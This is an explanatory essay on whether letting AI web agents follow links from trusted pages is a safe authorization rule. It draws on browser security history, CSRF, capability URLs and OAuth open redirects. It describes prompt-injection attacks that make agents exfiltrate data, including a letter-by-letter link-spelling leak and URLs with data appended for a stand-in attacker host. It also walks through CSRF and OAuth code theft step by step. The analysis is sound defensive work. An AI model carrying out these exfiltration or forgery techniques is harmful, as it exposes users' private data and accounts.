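# Letting Web Agents Follow Links from Trusted Pages: Hyperlinks as an Authorization Rule

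## How links can decide what an agent may do

A web agent is an AI model that opens web pages, and sometimes clicks, types or submits forms, to carry out a task for a user. It reads text written by strangers and often holds information the user would not want them to have. Its developers therefore need a rule about which pages it may open. One such rule lets the agent open an address if the user supplied it or if it is linked from a page the agent is already allowed to open.

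A user gives an agent the address of a town library's page on evening classes and asks which pottery class costs least, clay included. The page lists four classes, but their fees are on four other pages, two on the library's site and two on the teachers' own websites. An agent that may open only the typed address can't answer the question, while one that may open any address could also open one that a thief made up. Letting the agent follow links from the library's page is probably a sensible compromise for this task, but if one of the teachers' sites has a comment section, strangers could post links there that the agent might also be allowed to follow.

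### What a request gives away

The model has no direct access to the network. It can only write requests, such as a request to open an address, which the software around it, called the harness, carries out or refuses. *WebGPT* (Nakano, Hilton and colleagues, 2021) describes an early example, an OpenAI system that answered questions by browsing. The model could send a query to the Bing search engine, click on a listed link, scroll, search within a page, quote a passage, go back and stop. The harness treated any other output as an invalid action and ignored it. Because there was no command for typing an address, the model could reach a page only through a search result or a link, whatever it wrote.

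In the address (or URL) `library.example/classes/pottery?term=autumn`, the host is `library.example`, the path is `/classes/pottery`, and the query is everything after the question mark. A scheme, usually https, comes before the host, and a port number sometimes follows it. The scheme, host and port together make up the origin, which browsers use to keep sites apart. The host determines which server receives the request. That server receives the full path and query, which need not correspond to any file there, because whoever runs the server can have it accept any string.

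That makes the address a way to send data as well as request it. In the standard example, given in OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026), an attacker gets a model to request `attacker.example/collect?data=` with private data added to the end, then reads that data in the server's log. This is called exfiltration through a URL, where exfiltration means moving private data to someone who should not have it. The attacker has the data as soon as the request arrives, whatever page comes back. The agent may also make the request in the background, when it loads an image or previews a link, so the user may never notice.

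Web addresses could leak private data before agents existed. Jacobs (2004), in *URIs, Addressability, and the use of HTTP GET and POST*, imagined a bank that puts the customer's account number in the address of the account page. When the customer follows a link from that page to an advertiser, the number may appear in the advertiser's logs, because browsers can send the address of the page the visitor came from.

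A newer risk is that text on a page can cause the agent visiting it to send out private data. Prompt injection is text in the content an agent reads that the model wrongly treats as an instruction. *Silent Egress* (2026) describes a full attack, which begins when a user asks for a summary of a page. The system automatically previews the page and gives the model its text, including the attacker's instructions. The model then calls a network tool with values the attacker chose, which sends private material to the attacker's server, and the user still gets a good summary. In some systems the user does not need to ask for a summary, because the agent previews any address that comes up in conversation.

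A server can answer a request with a redirect, an instruction to go to another address. Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke (2022), in *3xx Redirection*, define these replies as ones that call for further action from the browser. The server usually gives the new address in a field called Location. If a harness checks the address the model requested but then follows redirects without checking again, it never checks the address where the request ends up.

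### The rule as a growing set of pages

Draw every web page as a node, and every link as an arrow from the page that contains it to the page it leads to. Let R₀ be the set of seeds, the addresses that the harness trusts at the start. Each later set adds every page linked from the one before:

Rₙ₊₁ = Rₙ ∪ { v : some page u in Rₙ links to v }

One step along an arrow is a hop. In the library example, R₀ holds the page on evening classes, R₁ adds everything that page links to, and R₂ adds everything those pages link to. A link-following rule with a limit of n hops permits Rₙ. Without a limit, it permits the union of all these sets, called the reachable set, which contains every page that can be reached from a seed by following any number of links. A redirect also counts as an arrow if the harness follows it.

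A real harness has no map of the web, so it adds a page's links to its list of permitted addresses only when the agent opens that page. At any moment the list is much shorter than the reachable set, but the agent can get to any address in the set by opening the pages that lead to it. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation described a rule of this kind for Claude models. Anthropic has since tightened the rule, so the tool no longer follows links found in the pages it fetches.

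The seeds may also be unsafe, because a person may not have typed them. The software developer Simon Willison (2025), in *Claude API*, pointed out that applications often paste untrusted material, such as an incoming document, into what the model receives as the user's message. If the harness trusts every address in that message, R₀ can contain an attacker's address before the agent follows any links.

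Suppose an attacker controls one page p in the reachable set and can put any links on it. The attacker can then make any address reachable, one hop beyond p, by linking to it from p. The address may be on the attacker's own server, on a newspaper's site or on a machine inside the network of the user's employer. The unlimited rule therefore permits every address the attacker can name. Without such a page, the rule would permit only addresses that other people chose to link to. The user's protection therefore depends on every page in the reachable set, and nobody has listed those pages.

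An attacker who doesn't control a page at the outset needs only a comment containing one link to a site the attacker owns. This adds one hop, and the rest of the argument is the same.

The addresses that matter most are those that contain the user's secret. An attacker who does not know the secret can still publish such an address by publishing links for all the possibilities. For example, a page offers 26 links, one for each letter, and asks the agent to spell the user's surname. The agent follows the link for M, and the server replies with a newly generated page of 26 more links, from MA to MZ. Every address the agent requests was already on a permitted page, so the harness has no reason to refuse, and after six hops the server's log contains a six-letter surname. Willison (2026) reported a working attack of this form against Claude. A choice among m links reveals log₂ m bits, which is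 about 4.7 bits for 26 links and 10 bits for a thousand.

A limit on hops helps less than one would expect. If the limit is n, an attacker who controls a page at distance n−1 or less can still link to any address they can name, which makes it permitted. Only a page at distance n can't be used this way. The limit also doesn't cap how much leaks, because the agent can return to the same page of 26 links and choose again, leaking another letter on each visit without lengthening the chain. A cap on total requests would bound the leak but cut off long honest tasks. Trust could also weaken with distance from the seeds, as it does in TrustRank for web search.

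### A worked example

The set of permitted pages grows quickly with each hop. If there is one seed, every page has 50 links, and all the links lead to different pages, the rule permits 1 + 50 + 2,500 = 2,551 pages after two hops. Suppose each page independently has a 1 in 1,000 chance of being open to attackers, meaning that an outsider can place links on it. The probability that all 2,551 pages are closed is then 0.999^2551, or about 0.078, so the chance that at least one is open is about 92%.

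| Hops allowed | Pages permitted | Chance that at least one is open to attackers |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | 1 | 0.1% |
| 1 | 51 | 5% |
| 2 | 2,551 | 92% |
| 3 | 127,551 | over 99.99% |

The figure of 50 links is realistic, since HTTP Archive's 2025 web survey found that the median desktop page had 43 links to its own site and six to other sites. The assumption that they all lead to different pages is unrealistic, because the pages of one site repeat the same menus and link to each other. If we count only the links that leave a site, and treat each site as a single node, there are 43 sites within two hops of the seed instead of 2,551 pages. The number still grows quickly, but later, reaching 1,555 sites within four hops.

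The result depends heavily on the assumption of independence, which is the most artificial one. Comment sections belong to whole sites, so open pages cluster. If the 2,551 pages belonged to 51 sites of about 50 pages each, each site might have a one in 1,000 chance of being wholly open and otherwise be wholly closed. The chance of meeting an open page would then fall from 92% to about 5%. If a user starts the agent on a discussion forum, however, the chance is 100% before the agent follows any links.

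The rate of one in 1,000 is invented. The nearest measurement, which is rough, is of a label that site owners can put on links from users' posts. HTTP Archive found it on 0.6% of desktop pages and 0.5% of mobile pages. The share of pages where an attacker could leave a working link might be higher, because many sites with comments never use the label, or lower, because many that use it moderate what people post. The two-hop chance is practically 100% if one page in 200 is open, and about 23% if one in 10,000 is.

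Finally, the 92% is the chance that the rule permits at least one open page, and an agent looking up pottery fees will visit perhaps ten of the 2,551 pages. If it picked those ten at random, its chance of landing on an open page would be only 1%. But agents choose links that look useful for the task, and an attacker can write such a link.

### Three things a link might show

When a harness treats a link as permission, it may be taking the link as evidence that the address carries no secret, that the linked content is trustworthy, or that the user permits an action there. People who speak of a "trusted link" tend not to distinguish between these.

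There can be quite good evidence that an address contains no secrets. If somebody wrote the address down before the conversation began, and had no access to the user's data, then the address cannot contain that data. OpenAI uses a version of this reasoning when it treats addresses that were already public, independently of any user's conversation, as much less likely to hold private information. The reasoning depends on when the address was created and who wrote it, not on the reputation of the page that links to it. An old link on a spammer's page therefore passes the test. A link on the user's own bank page may fail it, because the bank's server generated that page for this customer and may have put the account number in the address. This matters because, as Anthropic warns developers, publishers may retain any parameters in an address that Claude fetches.

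An agent can leak information even through old public addresses if it chooses which ones to request. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on a security research blog, notes that anyone with a moderately large website probably has 36 indexed pages already, enough to assign one to each letter and digit. The sequence of requests can then spell out a secret that no single address contains.

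A link is poor evidence that the content it leads to is trustworthy. The librarian who linked to a pottery teacher's site may have looked at it once, years ago, and the teacher can change it at any time. Visitors may be able to add to it as well. *Mind the Web* (2025) reports tests on a harmless city-guide website that its researchers had built. Malicious text there called the page "deprecated" and linked to an "updated" version, and the agent left for the BBC's site. In another test, an agent called Browser Use was asked for a summary, but a visitor's comment led it to open the hosts file on the user's computer (a list that matches the names of machines to their network addresses) and send its contents to the attacker's server. OpenAI states that its own check of addresses does not guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions.

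A link is no evidence that the user wants the agent to act on the page it leads to. In the library example, the user asked what the classes cost, and the link to the enrolment form showed only that the form existed. In a third test from *Mind the Web*, an agent called Do Browser followed instructions embedded in a page and published a Twitter post in which the user admitted to stealing money. Twitter is an ordinary site for an agent to visit, so a harness that checked only addresses could not have detected that this post was wrong.

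### Reading and acting

The web has long had a convention that separates reading from acting. Following a link normally sends a GET request, which asks for a page, while a form that changes something should send a POST request. Jacobs, writing for the World Wide Web Consortium's architecture group, stated the principle as "agents do not incur obligations by following links." Jacobs gives the example of subscribing to a mailing list. The confirmation email should link to a page with a button that sends the POST request. If opening the link is enough to complete the subscription, a mail program that loads pages in advance will subscribe people without their knowledge, and Jacobs considers the site at fault.

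Sites do not always follow the convention that GET requests should not change data. In 2005 Google released Web Accelerator, a program that loaded links before the user clicked on them. Willison (2005), in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs*, described how it did this inside password-protected applications, in effect clicking every "delete this" link and bypassing the warnings developers had added. Willison at first blamed Google but then changed his mind, reasoning that an application that deletes things on a GET request was already unsafe, since any malicious page could trigger the same links as the signed-in user.

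Under a link-following rule, permission to open an address is limited to reading only if the site there follows the convention that GET requests don't change anything. A harness can refuse to submit forms, which removes most ways of acting, but it cannot tell from the outside whether a given GET request will fetch a record or erase it. This is a concern given the all-or-nothing result, because the addresses an attacker can name include those on other people's systems. Jacobs described a malicious page on the public web that links to a machine behind a company's firewall. Someone inside the company who follows the link unwittingly triggers a function on that machine.

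### Why anyone would use such a rule

Despite these objections, there are good reasons for the rule. Browsing depends on following links. The agent in the library example needs the four other pages, and neither the user nor the developer could have listed them in advance. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026) argues that a fixed list of domains would severely limit systems whose value comes from wide access to outside knowledge. OpenAI adds that strict lists produce frequent warnings, and that users learn to click through these without thinking.

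A link-following rule at least checks each address, whereas current agent frameworks mostly grant permission tool by tool, according to *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data*. A user who approves "web search" approves every address and query the tool will ever send. The interface also often cuts the address short, which hides any data encoded at the end.

The harness can enforce this rule by looking up each address in a list, which requires no judgement about whether a page is malicious. A model that made that judgement would be open to the same tricks as the model it protects. Suppose an injected instruction has fooled the model completely, and the model appends the user's email address to `attacker.example/collect?data=` and requests the result. No permitted page contains that exact address, so the harness refuses. Willison judged that the ban on addresses composed by the model was the part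 of Anthropic's rule that protected most against common exfiltration attacks. The spelling attack gets around this ban, but it requires a purpose-built site and an agent that follows link after link, which is more work than planting one sentence.

Nakano and colleagues made an early argument for limiting an agent to links. They feared that a model with access to forms might edit Wikipedia to create a reliable-looking source for its own answer. They rated the risk from such side effects "very low" because their model could only query Bing and follow existing links. This was convincing for their system, which answered questions taken mostly from a Reddit forum, had no forms to fill in, and worked without access to anyone's mailbox or saved files. Agents that remember their users' earlier conversations, or that run in a browser where the user is signed in, meet any of these conditions only if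 they are deliberately designed to. Nakano and colleagues also argued that the burden of proof for giving a model access to the web should grow with the model's capabilities.

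## Browsers: following a link and acting as the user

Nakano and colleagues' system visited every site without signing in. Most people use a browser that is signed in to their bank and email, and the same browser opens pages written by people who would like to get into those accounts. In the mid-1990s, browser makers settled what a link could do under those conditions. Any page may link to any address, but the link doesn't give that page the right to read what is there. If a pottery teacher's site links to the library's staff rota, a librarian who clicks the link will see the rota, but the teacher's site cannot read it.

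### What counts as the same origin

This rule is called the same-origin policy. *The Web Origin Concept* (Barth, 2011), written for the internet's standards body, defines two addresses as having the same origin if their schemes, hosts and ports all match. The table compares five addresses with `https://library.example/classes/pottery`.

| Address | Same origin? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `https://library.example/opening-hours` | Yes | Only the path differs |
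| `https://library.example:443/classes/pottery` | Yes | 443 is the default port for https |
| `http://library.example/classes/pottery` | No | Different scheme |
| `https://www.library.example/classes/pottery` | No | Different host |
| `https://library.example:8443/classes/pottery` | No | Different port |

The scheme matters because someone on the same café network can tamper with an unencrypted http page. If that page shared an origin with the encrypted version of the site, its scripts could read the encrypted one. The path doesn't matter, which is sometimes a problem. Barth gives the example of a university that puts every student's pages under one host, so they share an origin and the students' scripts can read each other's pages. Browsers could in principle treat each address as its own origin, but web applications consist of many files that have to work together.

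A script from one origin can't normally read a page from another. The exception is a server that opts in, by telling the browser which other origins may read its replies. Permission to read therefore comes from the site that holds the data, whoever links to it. (Agents built into browsers can defeat the policy by carrying text between sites, as Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, demonstrated.)

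Some references in a page grant privileges to what they load. If the library's page loads a script from `stats.example`, the browser runs that script with all the privileges of the library's page, but an image from the same address would get none. The browser uses the page's code to distinguish the two. A harness that gathers every address on a page into one list of permitted destinations loses that distinction.

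### Where the policy came from

Netscape introduced JavaScript, the scripting language for web pages, in late 1995 with its browser Navigator 2.0. *Security Holes and Security Hobbles*, a section of the programmers' manual *JavaScript: The Definitive Guide* from about 1997, lists some attacks that malicious pages could carry out at the time. A page could open a window too small to notice, load the browser's own list of stored files into it, read the links on that list, and send the user's browsing history to a server through a hidden form. Loading a `file:///` address in the window instead revealed the names of the folders on the user's disk.

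Netscape at first patched these holes one at a time, and people kept finding more. Navigator 2.0.2 replaced much of the patching with a general rule that a script could not read a window whose contents came from a different server. The rule also prevented scripts on the public internet from opening a window inside a company's network and browsing there. Internet Explorer 3.0 had no such rule when the manual appeared. By the fourth edition of *JavaScript* (Flanagan, 2001), the rule was called the same-origin policy and covered host, port and protocol.

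It broke some legitimate programs. According to the manual's *The Data-Tainting Security Model*, these included scripts that crawl the web by following links from a starting page, as a link-following agent does. Netscape therefore tried an alternative called data tainting, which let a script read private data but labelled the data with the server it belonged to. The browser asked the user before sending that data to any other server, and it counted requesting an address as sending data.

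It was hard to keep the labels attached, because a script could test a private value and set a new, unlabelled variable to match. This copied the secret without copying the labelled data. The page of 26 links leaks a letter in much the same way, through the agent's choice of link. Netscape responded by labelling the script itself once it had made such a test. But the system prompted users so often that Netscape left it off by default, and browsers kept the blunter rule about reading. Barth records that models of this kind proved difficult to implement at the time.

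### The requests still go out

The same-origin policy does little to stop a page from sending requests to other origins because, as Barth explains, blocking them would prevent users from following links. These requests are dangerous because of cookies. A cookie is a short piece of text that a site gives the browser, often when the user signs in. The browser sends it back with later requests so that the site can identify the user. For many years, browsers attached the cookie no matter which page caused the request.

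Cross-site request forgery exploits this. Suppose a bank lets customers transfer money by submitting a form to `bank.example/transfer` and identifies them only by their cookie.

1. A customer signs in to the bank, and the browser stores the bank's cookie.
2. In another tab, the customer opens a page that belongs to an attacker.
3. That page contains a hidden form addressed to `bank.example/transfer`, with the attacker's account number and an amount already filled in. A script submits it as soon as the page loads.
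4. The browser sends the form to the bank and attaches the customer's cookie.
5. The bank recognises the customer and moves the money.

The attacker's page cannot read the bank's reply, but the transfer has already gone through. Using a POST request, as web conventions recommend for transfers, does not prevent the attack, because a page can submit a form to another site. If the bank accepted transfers by GET, the attacker would not need a form and could use the transfer URL as the source of an image on the page.

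Willison linked to a description of the attack in May 2005 and commented, "Somehow this vulnerability is news to me," although the underlying mistake was much older.

### The confused deputy

Norm Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) tells a "nearly true story" about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler, the program that translates users' code for the machine, kept statistics in a file in its own directory, so staff had given it a licence to write files there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the company's billing file, which was in the same directory. The user had no right to change that file, but the compiler did. The operating system checked the compiler's licence, so the compiler wrote its debugging output over the bills.

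Hardy traced the accident to the compiler having two sources of authority, the user who ran it and the licence, and no way to specify which one to use when it opened a file. A program in this position is a confused deputy, meaning that it uses its own authority for someone who lacks it. The online discussion *Confused Deputy* reduces the problem to two conditions: a resource's name does not carry the authority needed to use it, and the program applies its own permission implicitly.

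A forged bank transfer meets both conditions. Anyone can write the URL `bank.example/transfer`, but writing it gives them no right to the customer's money. The browser then adds the customer's cookie to the request without checking who initiated it.

The obvious fixes failed at Tymshare. The compiler could not refuse to write to files in its own directory, since some users had legitimate reasons to write there. It also could not carry a list of sensitive files, because the list would need changing whenever someone added one. The staff tried a command that let the compiler "switch hats" between its two authorities, then found that some programs needed more than two. The last time Hardy wrote down the conditions for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s. A harness that gains an exception every time a link turns out to be dangerous could easily become just as complicated.

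### Tokens and SameSite cookies

The older defense against request forgery is a secret token. The bank includes a long random number, tied to the customer's session, in the transfer form it sends, and refuses any transfer that arrives without that number. The attacker can copy the rest of the form but cannot read the number, because the same-origin policy keeps the attacker's page from reading the bank's. The defense fails if the attacker can get a script into one of the bank's own pages, because that script can read the token.

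SameSite cookies move the check into the browser. A site can mark a cookie "Strict", and the browser then leaves it off every request that starts on another site. This is safe, but a customer who follows a link to the bank from webmail arrives signed out. With the "Lax" setting, the browser sends the cookie when the user follows an ordinary link, but still leaves it off forms that other sites submit by POST and images they load. In 2020 Chrome began treating unmarked cookies as Lax.

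A "site" here is broader than an origin and usually means the registered domain with everything under it. `students.example.edu` and `grades.example.edu` count as one site, so a student's page could still send forged requests to the grading system with the cookie attached. Barth had advised against drawing security boundaries this way, partly because where a registered domain begins depends on convention, so software has to consult lists that are hard to keep up to date.

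The Lax setting is designed for sites where following a link changes nothing. If a GET request can move money or delete a file, an attacker can trigger it just by getting the user to follow a link.

### Google Web Accelerator

Tokens and SameSite cookies are meant to catch requests that start on another site. Google Web Accelerator, which loaded links in advance, was not malicious but caused similar damage by following links on the sites' own pages.

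Techdirt's *An Ever Impatient Google* (2005) reported the launch of Google's Web Accelerator on May 4. The next day, a few users of Backpack, an online organiser made by the software company 37signals, told the company that their pages were disappearing. Jason Fried's *Google Web Accelerator* (2005) traced the losses to the accelerator, which had been requesting Backpack's "delete" links along with all the others.

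Backpack had a password and a confirmation box, and neither stopped the accelerator. The accelerator ran on the user's own computer and fetched pages as the signed-in user, so the password did not keep it out. The confirmation box, which asked "Are you sure you want to delete this?", came from a script that ran when somebody clicked the link. The accelerator read the address out of the page and requested it directly, so the script never ran and Backpack's server deleted the page. A secret token in the link would not have helped either, since the accelerator would have copied it with the rest of the address.

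Readers who replied to Fried reported similar problems. One had lost sales leads from a company database. Another could not use webmail because the accelerator followed the sign-out link as soon as they signed in. A third pointed out that Blogger, which Google owned, also deleted comments through a plain link. However, some who tested the program could only get it to fetch links that a page had marked for prefetching.

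HTTP, the protocol browsers and servers use, defines GET as a "safe" method. thoughtbot's *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident* quotes a definition of safe methods as essentially read-only, meaning that the sender neither requests nor expects any change on the server. The server may still change something, such as by adding a line to its log. But the 1999 version of the standard, which several of the readers quoted, says that "the user did not request the side-effects" and cannot be held accountable for them. Search engines depend on this convention because they request millions of addresses that no person has looked at, which nobody could do responsibly if GET requests could have any effect at all.

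David Heinemeier Hansson of 37signals disagreed that the sites were at fault. The standard says that GET requests "SHOULD NOT" do more than retrieve, which is weaker than "MUST NOT" and allows exceptions for good reason. Many developers had thought a password was a good enough reason, because crawlers had never gone behind one. Heinemeier Hansson's post that day, *Google's Accelerator in need of a recall*, compared the program to a faulty car. The programmer Ian Bicking likewise thought Google should have designed for the web as it was, and noted that the browser maker Mozilla prefetched only links that pages had marked for prefetching. Bicking wrote in *Google at it again* that a later version of the accelerator again followed "delete" and "logout" links.

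Ryan Tomayko, another of the readers, agreed that Google should hold back for the moment, but warned developers against relying on that restraint: "This type of service by intermediation is only going to grow." He was right. Although the sites had broken the convention, Google was careless to test it on other people's data when so many sites were known to break it. Anyone who builds a link-following agent for signed-in users faces the same choice, and has less excuse for being surprised when sites break the convention.

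37signals dealt with the problem by refusing requests with a header that marked them as prefetches, but this works only when the program sends that header. Limiting a program to GET doesn't always limit what it sends either, because if it runs the scripts on the pages it opens, those scripts can send requests of their own. According to http.dev's *HTTP Methods*, Google's crawlers now use POST and several other methods as well as GET, and the less common ones come from scripts that run while the crawler renders a page.

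In HTTP, "safe" also refers only to the site's data, so a GET request that sends the user's secret to an attacker's server still counts as safe.

### When the link is the permission

Some links give permission to whoever holds them. Tennison's *Good Practices for Capability URLs*, guidance from the World Wide Web Consortium's architecture group, calls these capability URLs. In a password reset, for example, the user can't sign in, so the site emails a link containing a long random string, and anyone who opens that link before it expires can set a new password. Shared documents often work this way too. The polling site Doodle gives a poll's organiser two addresses, one to send to the participants and another for changing or deleting the poll.

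An ordinary link to a private page is useless to a stranger, because the server requires a cookie the stranger does not have. A capability URL needs no cookie, so its only protection is that the address is secret and hard to guess. If a site numbers its documents 1, 2, 3 and so on, an attacker can find one on the first try. Tennison recommends at least 120 random bits, which allows about 1.3 × 10³⁶ possibilities. If a site had a million such links in use and an attacker tried a billion addresses a second for a year, the chance of finding even one would be about one in 40 trillion.

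Leaks are a much bigger danger than guessing. Addresses appear in browser histories and server logs, and on the screen during presentations. They can also reach the next site the reader visits, as in Jacobs's bank example. Some browsers send the addresses their users visit to a central server that checks for fraud. Noah Mendelsohn, whose comments Meijer (2014) quotes, thought it a mistake to encourage capability URLs at all, because "the Web is not in general designed to preserve such URL secrecy." The group still published its advice, which concentrates on limiting the damage. Links should expire, and owners should be able to cancel them. A site can also issue a separate link to each person, so that cancelling one doesn't lock out the others.

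Tennison adds that opening a capability URL should not by itself delete or change anything, much as Jacobs had advised for confirmation emails. Jacob Hoffman-Andrews (2014), of the Electronic Frontier Foundation, replied that in practice, email links labeled "confirm email" or "unsubscribe" typically act as soon as someone opens them.

An agent allowed to follow any link in its user's inbox can confirm registrations and cancel subscriptions when it is only trying to read. It also sees password reset links and links to private documents. Anyone who has one of these links can use it, so an attacker only needs to get the agent to pass one on.

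### Passing on what you hold

Hardy wanted operating systems to work the way capability URLs do. A capability here is a reference that both identifies a file and authorizes its holder to use it. The compiler would hold one capability for its statistics file, and the user would give it another for the debugging output. A user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for that file to give the compiler, so the accident could not happen, and the compiler would not need to check file names.

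Programmers call the general approach object capabilities. An introduction on the blog Habitat Chronicles (2017) traces the idea to a 1966 paper by Dennis and Van Horn. A program can use only the objects it has references to, and it can pass on only references it holds. Receiving a reference is therefore good evidence of permission, because whoever passed it on had the same access. For example, the organiser of a meeting between several companies can send a poll's address to one person at each company, who forwards it to the right colleagues. The organiser doesn't need to know who those colleagues are.

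A link-following rule closely resembles this, with links in place of references. But on the web, people can pass on addresses they have no right to use. In the bank example, the attacker could write the transfer page's address as easily as the bank could, and the customer's cookie supplied the authority. If a harness treats such a link as permission and the agent is signed in as the user, the agent can be tricked into misusing its authority, as Tymshare's compiler was.

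The risk of following a link depends partly on what access the agent adds to the request. An agent with no cookies and no access to a private network can open only what the link's author could also open, though the author may still get it to read malicious instructions or reveal information it has. If the agent has the user's cookies or runs on a computer inside the user's company, a stranger's link can also make it send requests with the user's authority, even if the stranger has none.

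## Open redirects in sign-in systems and script policies

An address shows only where a request starts. Many sites have a page whose job is to send visitors on to somewhere else, and sometimes the link itself names the destination. If the library's site had such a page, its link to a pottery teacher's fees might look like this:

`https://library.example/leave?to=https://potter.example/fees`

When a browser follows this link, it first sends a request to `library.example`, whose server reads the address after `to=` and replies with a redirect. The browser then requests the fees page from `potter.example`. In *Best Current Practice for OAuth 2.0 Security*, Lodderstedt, Bradley and colleagues call such a page an open redirector if it forwards browsers to any address given in the link. Anyone can replace the teacher's address with another, and a program that checks only the first domain will approve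 the link because it still begins with `library.example`.

On the map of pages and arrows, an open redirector adds an arrow from the library's site to every address on the web. This does less damage if the harness permits only the exact addresses it has found on permitted pages, because an attacker still has to get the altered link onto one of those pages. But if the harness permits everything on `library.example`, the attacker can fool the model into writing the link itself, with the user's secret at the end. The same attack also works against AI products limited to approved domains.

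Sites keep these pages to show a message before a visitor leaves, to count clicks on each link, or to return users to the page they wanted before a login prompt interrupted them. A site can do this safely if it forwards only to addresses on an approved list, or only when it can verify that it wrote the link.

Some security teams rated open redirects as minor, but their argument is weak when software has already made a decision based on the first address, as happens in sign-in systems. They reasoned that the redirector reveals no data and changes nothing on the site. The obvious abuse is phishing, where a link appears to lead to a trusted site but opens a fake one, and attackers can do that with lookalike domains anyway. The argument is fair for people, who can at least check the address bar when they arrive.

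### Where a sign-in sends the code

OAuth is the system behind buttons such as "Sign in with Google". It lets a site (the client) use an account that somebody holds with another company (the provider). Suppose a user signs in to a pottery forum this way. Wang, Lau and colleagues, in *Make Redirection Evil Again*, a talk at the Black Hat security conference, set out the usual flow:

1. The forum redirects the user's browser to the provider. The address includes the forum's public ID and a redirect address, `https://forum.example/callback`, where the provider should send the browser afterwards.
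2. The provider asks the user to sign in and approve the forum, unless the user has already done both.
3. The provider redirects the browser to the redirect address with a temporary code on the end, such as `https://forum.example/callback?code=8f2k`.
4. The forum's server sends the code to the provider, along with a password of its own, and receives an access token. This lets it look up who the user is and sign them in.

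An attacker can write the address in step 1 because it contains nothing secret. If the provider did not check the redirect address, the attacker could set it to `attacker.example` and get the victim's browser to load the step 1 address. An image on a web page would be enough to trigger the request if the victim had already approved the forum. The code would then arrive at the attacker's server.

Redeeming the code requires the forum's password, so the attacker gets the forum to do it. They start their own sign-in at the forum and substitute the victim's code in step 3. The forum redeems the code and signs the attacker in as the victim.

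Providers therefore compare the redirect address with one that the client registered in advance. Some let clients register a pattern instead, which saves listing every address and lets the client add details that vary between sign-ins. Lodderstedt and colleagues give the example of `https://*.somesite.example/*`, which should cover every host under `somesite.example`. If the provider's software treats the first star as "any characters", the pattern also matches `https://attacker.example/.somesite.example`. Software that interprets the pattern correctly will still accept an abandoned subdomain that an attacker has taken over.

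An open redirector can defeat a pattern that covers only the client's own site. Suppose the provider accepts any address on `forum.example`, and the forum has a redirector at `forum.example/go?to=`. The attacker then submits `https://forum.example/go?to=https://attacker.example` as the redirect address, and the provider approves it.

Where the provider puts the secret then determines whether it reaches the attacker. A code in the query goes to the forum's redirector, which normally leaves it out when it forwards the browser. But a provider can also use the fragment, the part of an address after a `#`, which browsers don't send to servers. If the redirect's target address has no fragment, the browser adds the old one, so the fragment reaches `attacker.example`, where a script on the page can read it. OAuth's older implicit flow put the access token in the fragment, and some providers will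 put a code there if the request specifies it.

### The Covert Redirect dispute

In early May 2014 Wang Jing, a doctoral student in mathematics at Nanyang Technological University in Singapore, publicised this attack under the name "Covert Redirect". This was soon after Heartbleed, a bug in widely used encryption software that let attackers read servers' memory. Wang reported that "almost all major OAuth 2.0 and OpenID providers are affected" (OpenID is a related sign-in system), including Google, Facebook and Microsoft.

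Kerner (2014), in *Covert Redirect is No Heartbleed*, quoted that claim but rejected others' comparison with Heartbleed. iTnews' *'Covert Redirect' vulnerability affects OAuth 2.0, OpenID* reported a general view that the flaw was less serious but still a threat. This seems right, since an attacker needed a victim who would open a link or page, a provider that matched redirect addresses loosely, and a client with an open redirector. The attack was probably not new. In a message to a cryptography mailing list, *"Covert Redirect" vulnerability in OAuth, OpenID*, Hodges (2014) thought a 2012 paper on OpenID security had likely already discussed it.

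The bug was in client sites that ran open redirectors, and critics of the announcement said that those sites were at fault and OAuth itself was sound. But providers were better placed to fix it. Although a provider may serve thousands of clients and can't inspect every page they run, it can stop the attack for all of them by requiring the full registered address. OpenID Connect, a sign-in standard built on OAuth, had required this since February 2014.

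### Exact matching

Large providers took years to follow. Wang and colleagues report that PayPal enforced exact matching in 2015, and that Facebook offered it as an option in December 2017 before making it the default. In January 2025, Lodderstedt and colleagues published their recommendations as RFC 9700, the internet standards body's current advice on OAuth. Providers must now compare the two addresses character by character, except that the port number may vary for apps that receive the code on the user's own device. Clients and providers must also not run open redirectors.

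Wang and colleagues tested 50 providers and found 11 from which they could steal codes or tokens. All 11 were among the 22 that used patterns to match addresses. Most of the attacks relied on addresses that the provider's software and the browser interpreted differently, so the result is evidence against loose matching in general more than against open redirectors. After the researchers reported the flaws, only one provider switched to exact matching. The others patched their software, and the researchers immediately found ways around some of the patches.

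Other tests also found that providers checked redirect addresses poorly. Li, Chen and Mitchell (2018), in *Your Code Is My Code*, found that 19 of 27 leading providers would send a user's code to an attacker who altered part of the redirect address. Innocenti, Golinelli and colleagues (2023), in *OAuth 2.0 Redirect URI Validation Falls Short, Literally*, tested 16 providers and concluded that the guidance at the time was not specific enough. *A First Measurement Study on Authentication Security in Real-World Remote MCP Servers* (2026) lists the same problem among the flaws of newer software, servers that connect AI models to outside tools.

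Exact matching proves that a client registered the address, but the client may still be malicious. Some providers let anyone register a client automatically, so an attacker can register a phishing page and send people a genuine link to the provider. Even if the user refuses the request, the provider redirects them to the phishing page to report the refusal. Lodderstedt and colleagues therefore advise providers to redirect automatically only to addresses they trust.

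A redirect can also forward form data. After most redirects the browser sends a plain GET request, but a 307 response makes it repeat the original request, including anything the user typed into a form. If a provider used a 307 right after its login form, the browser would send the user's password to the client. An agent that submits forms could leak data the same way, even if the user approved the first destination.

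### Lists of approved script sources

Sites also use lists of approved addresses to control what their own pages load, mainly to defend against cross-site scripting. In this attack, someone gets a script into one of the site's pages, perhaps through a comment that the site failed to sanitize. The script runs with all the privileges of that page.

Content Security Policy (CSP) is a second line of defense against this. The site sends a policy with each page, and the browser enforces it. For example, the policy `script-src library.example maps.example` allows scripts only from those two hosts, so the browser blocks an injected reference to a script on `attacker.example`.

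A policy can also cover images and other files, which helps against exfiltration. However, *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), the World Wide Web Consortium's current draft, warns that this protection is only as strong as the least restrictive list of allowed sources. A page that accepts images from anywhere can still leak data, even if it blocks everything else.

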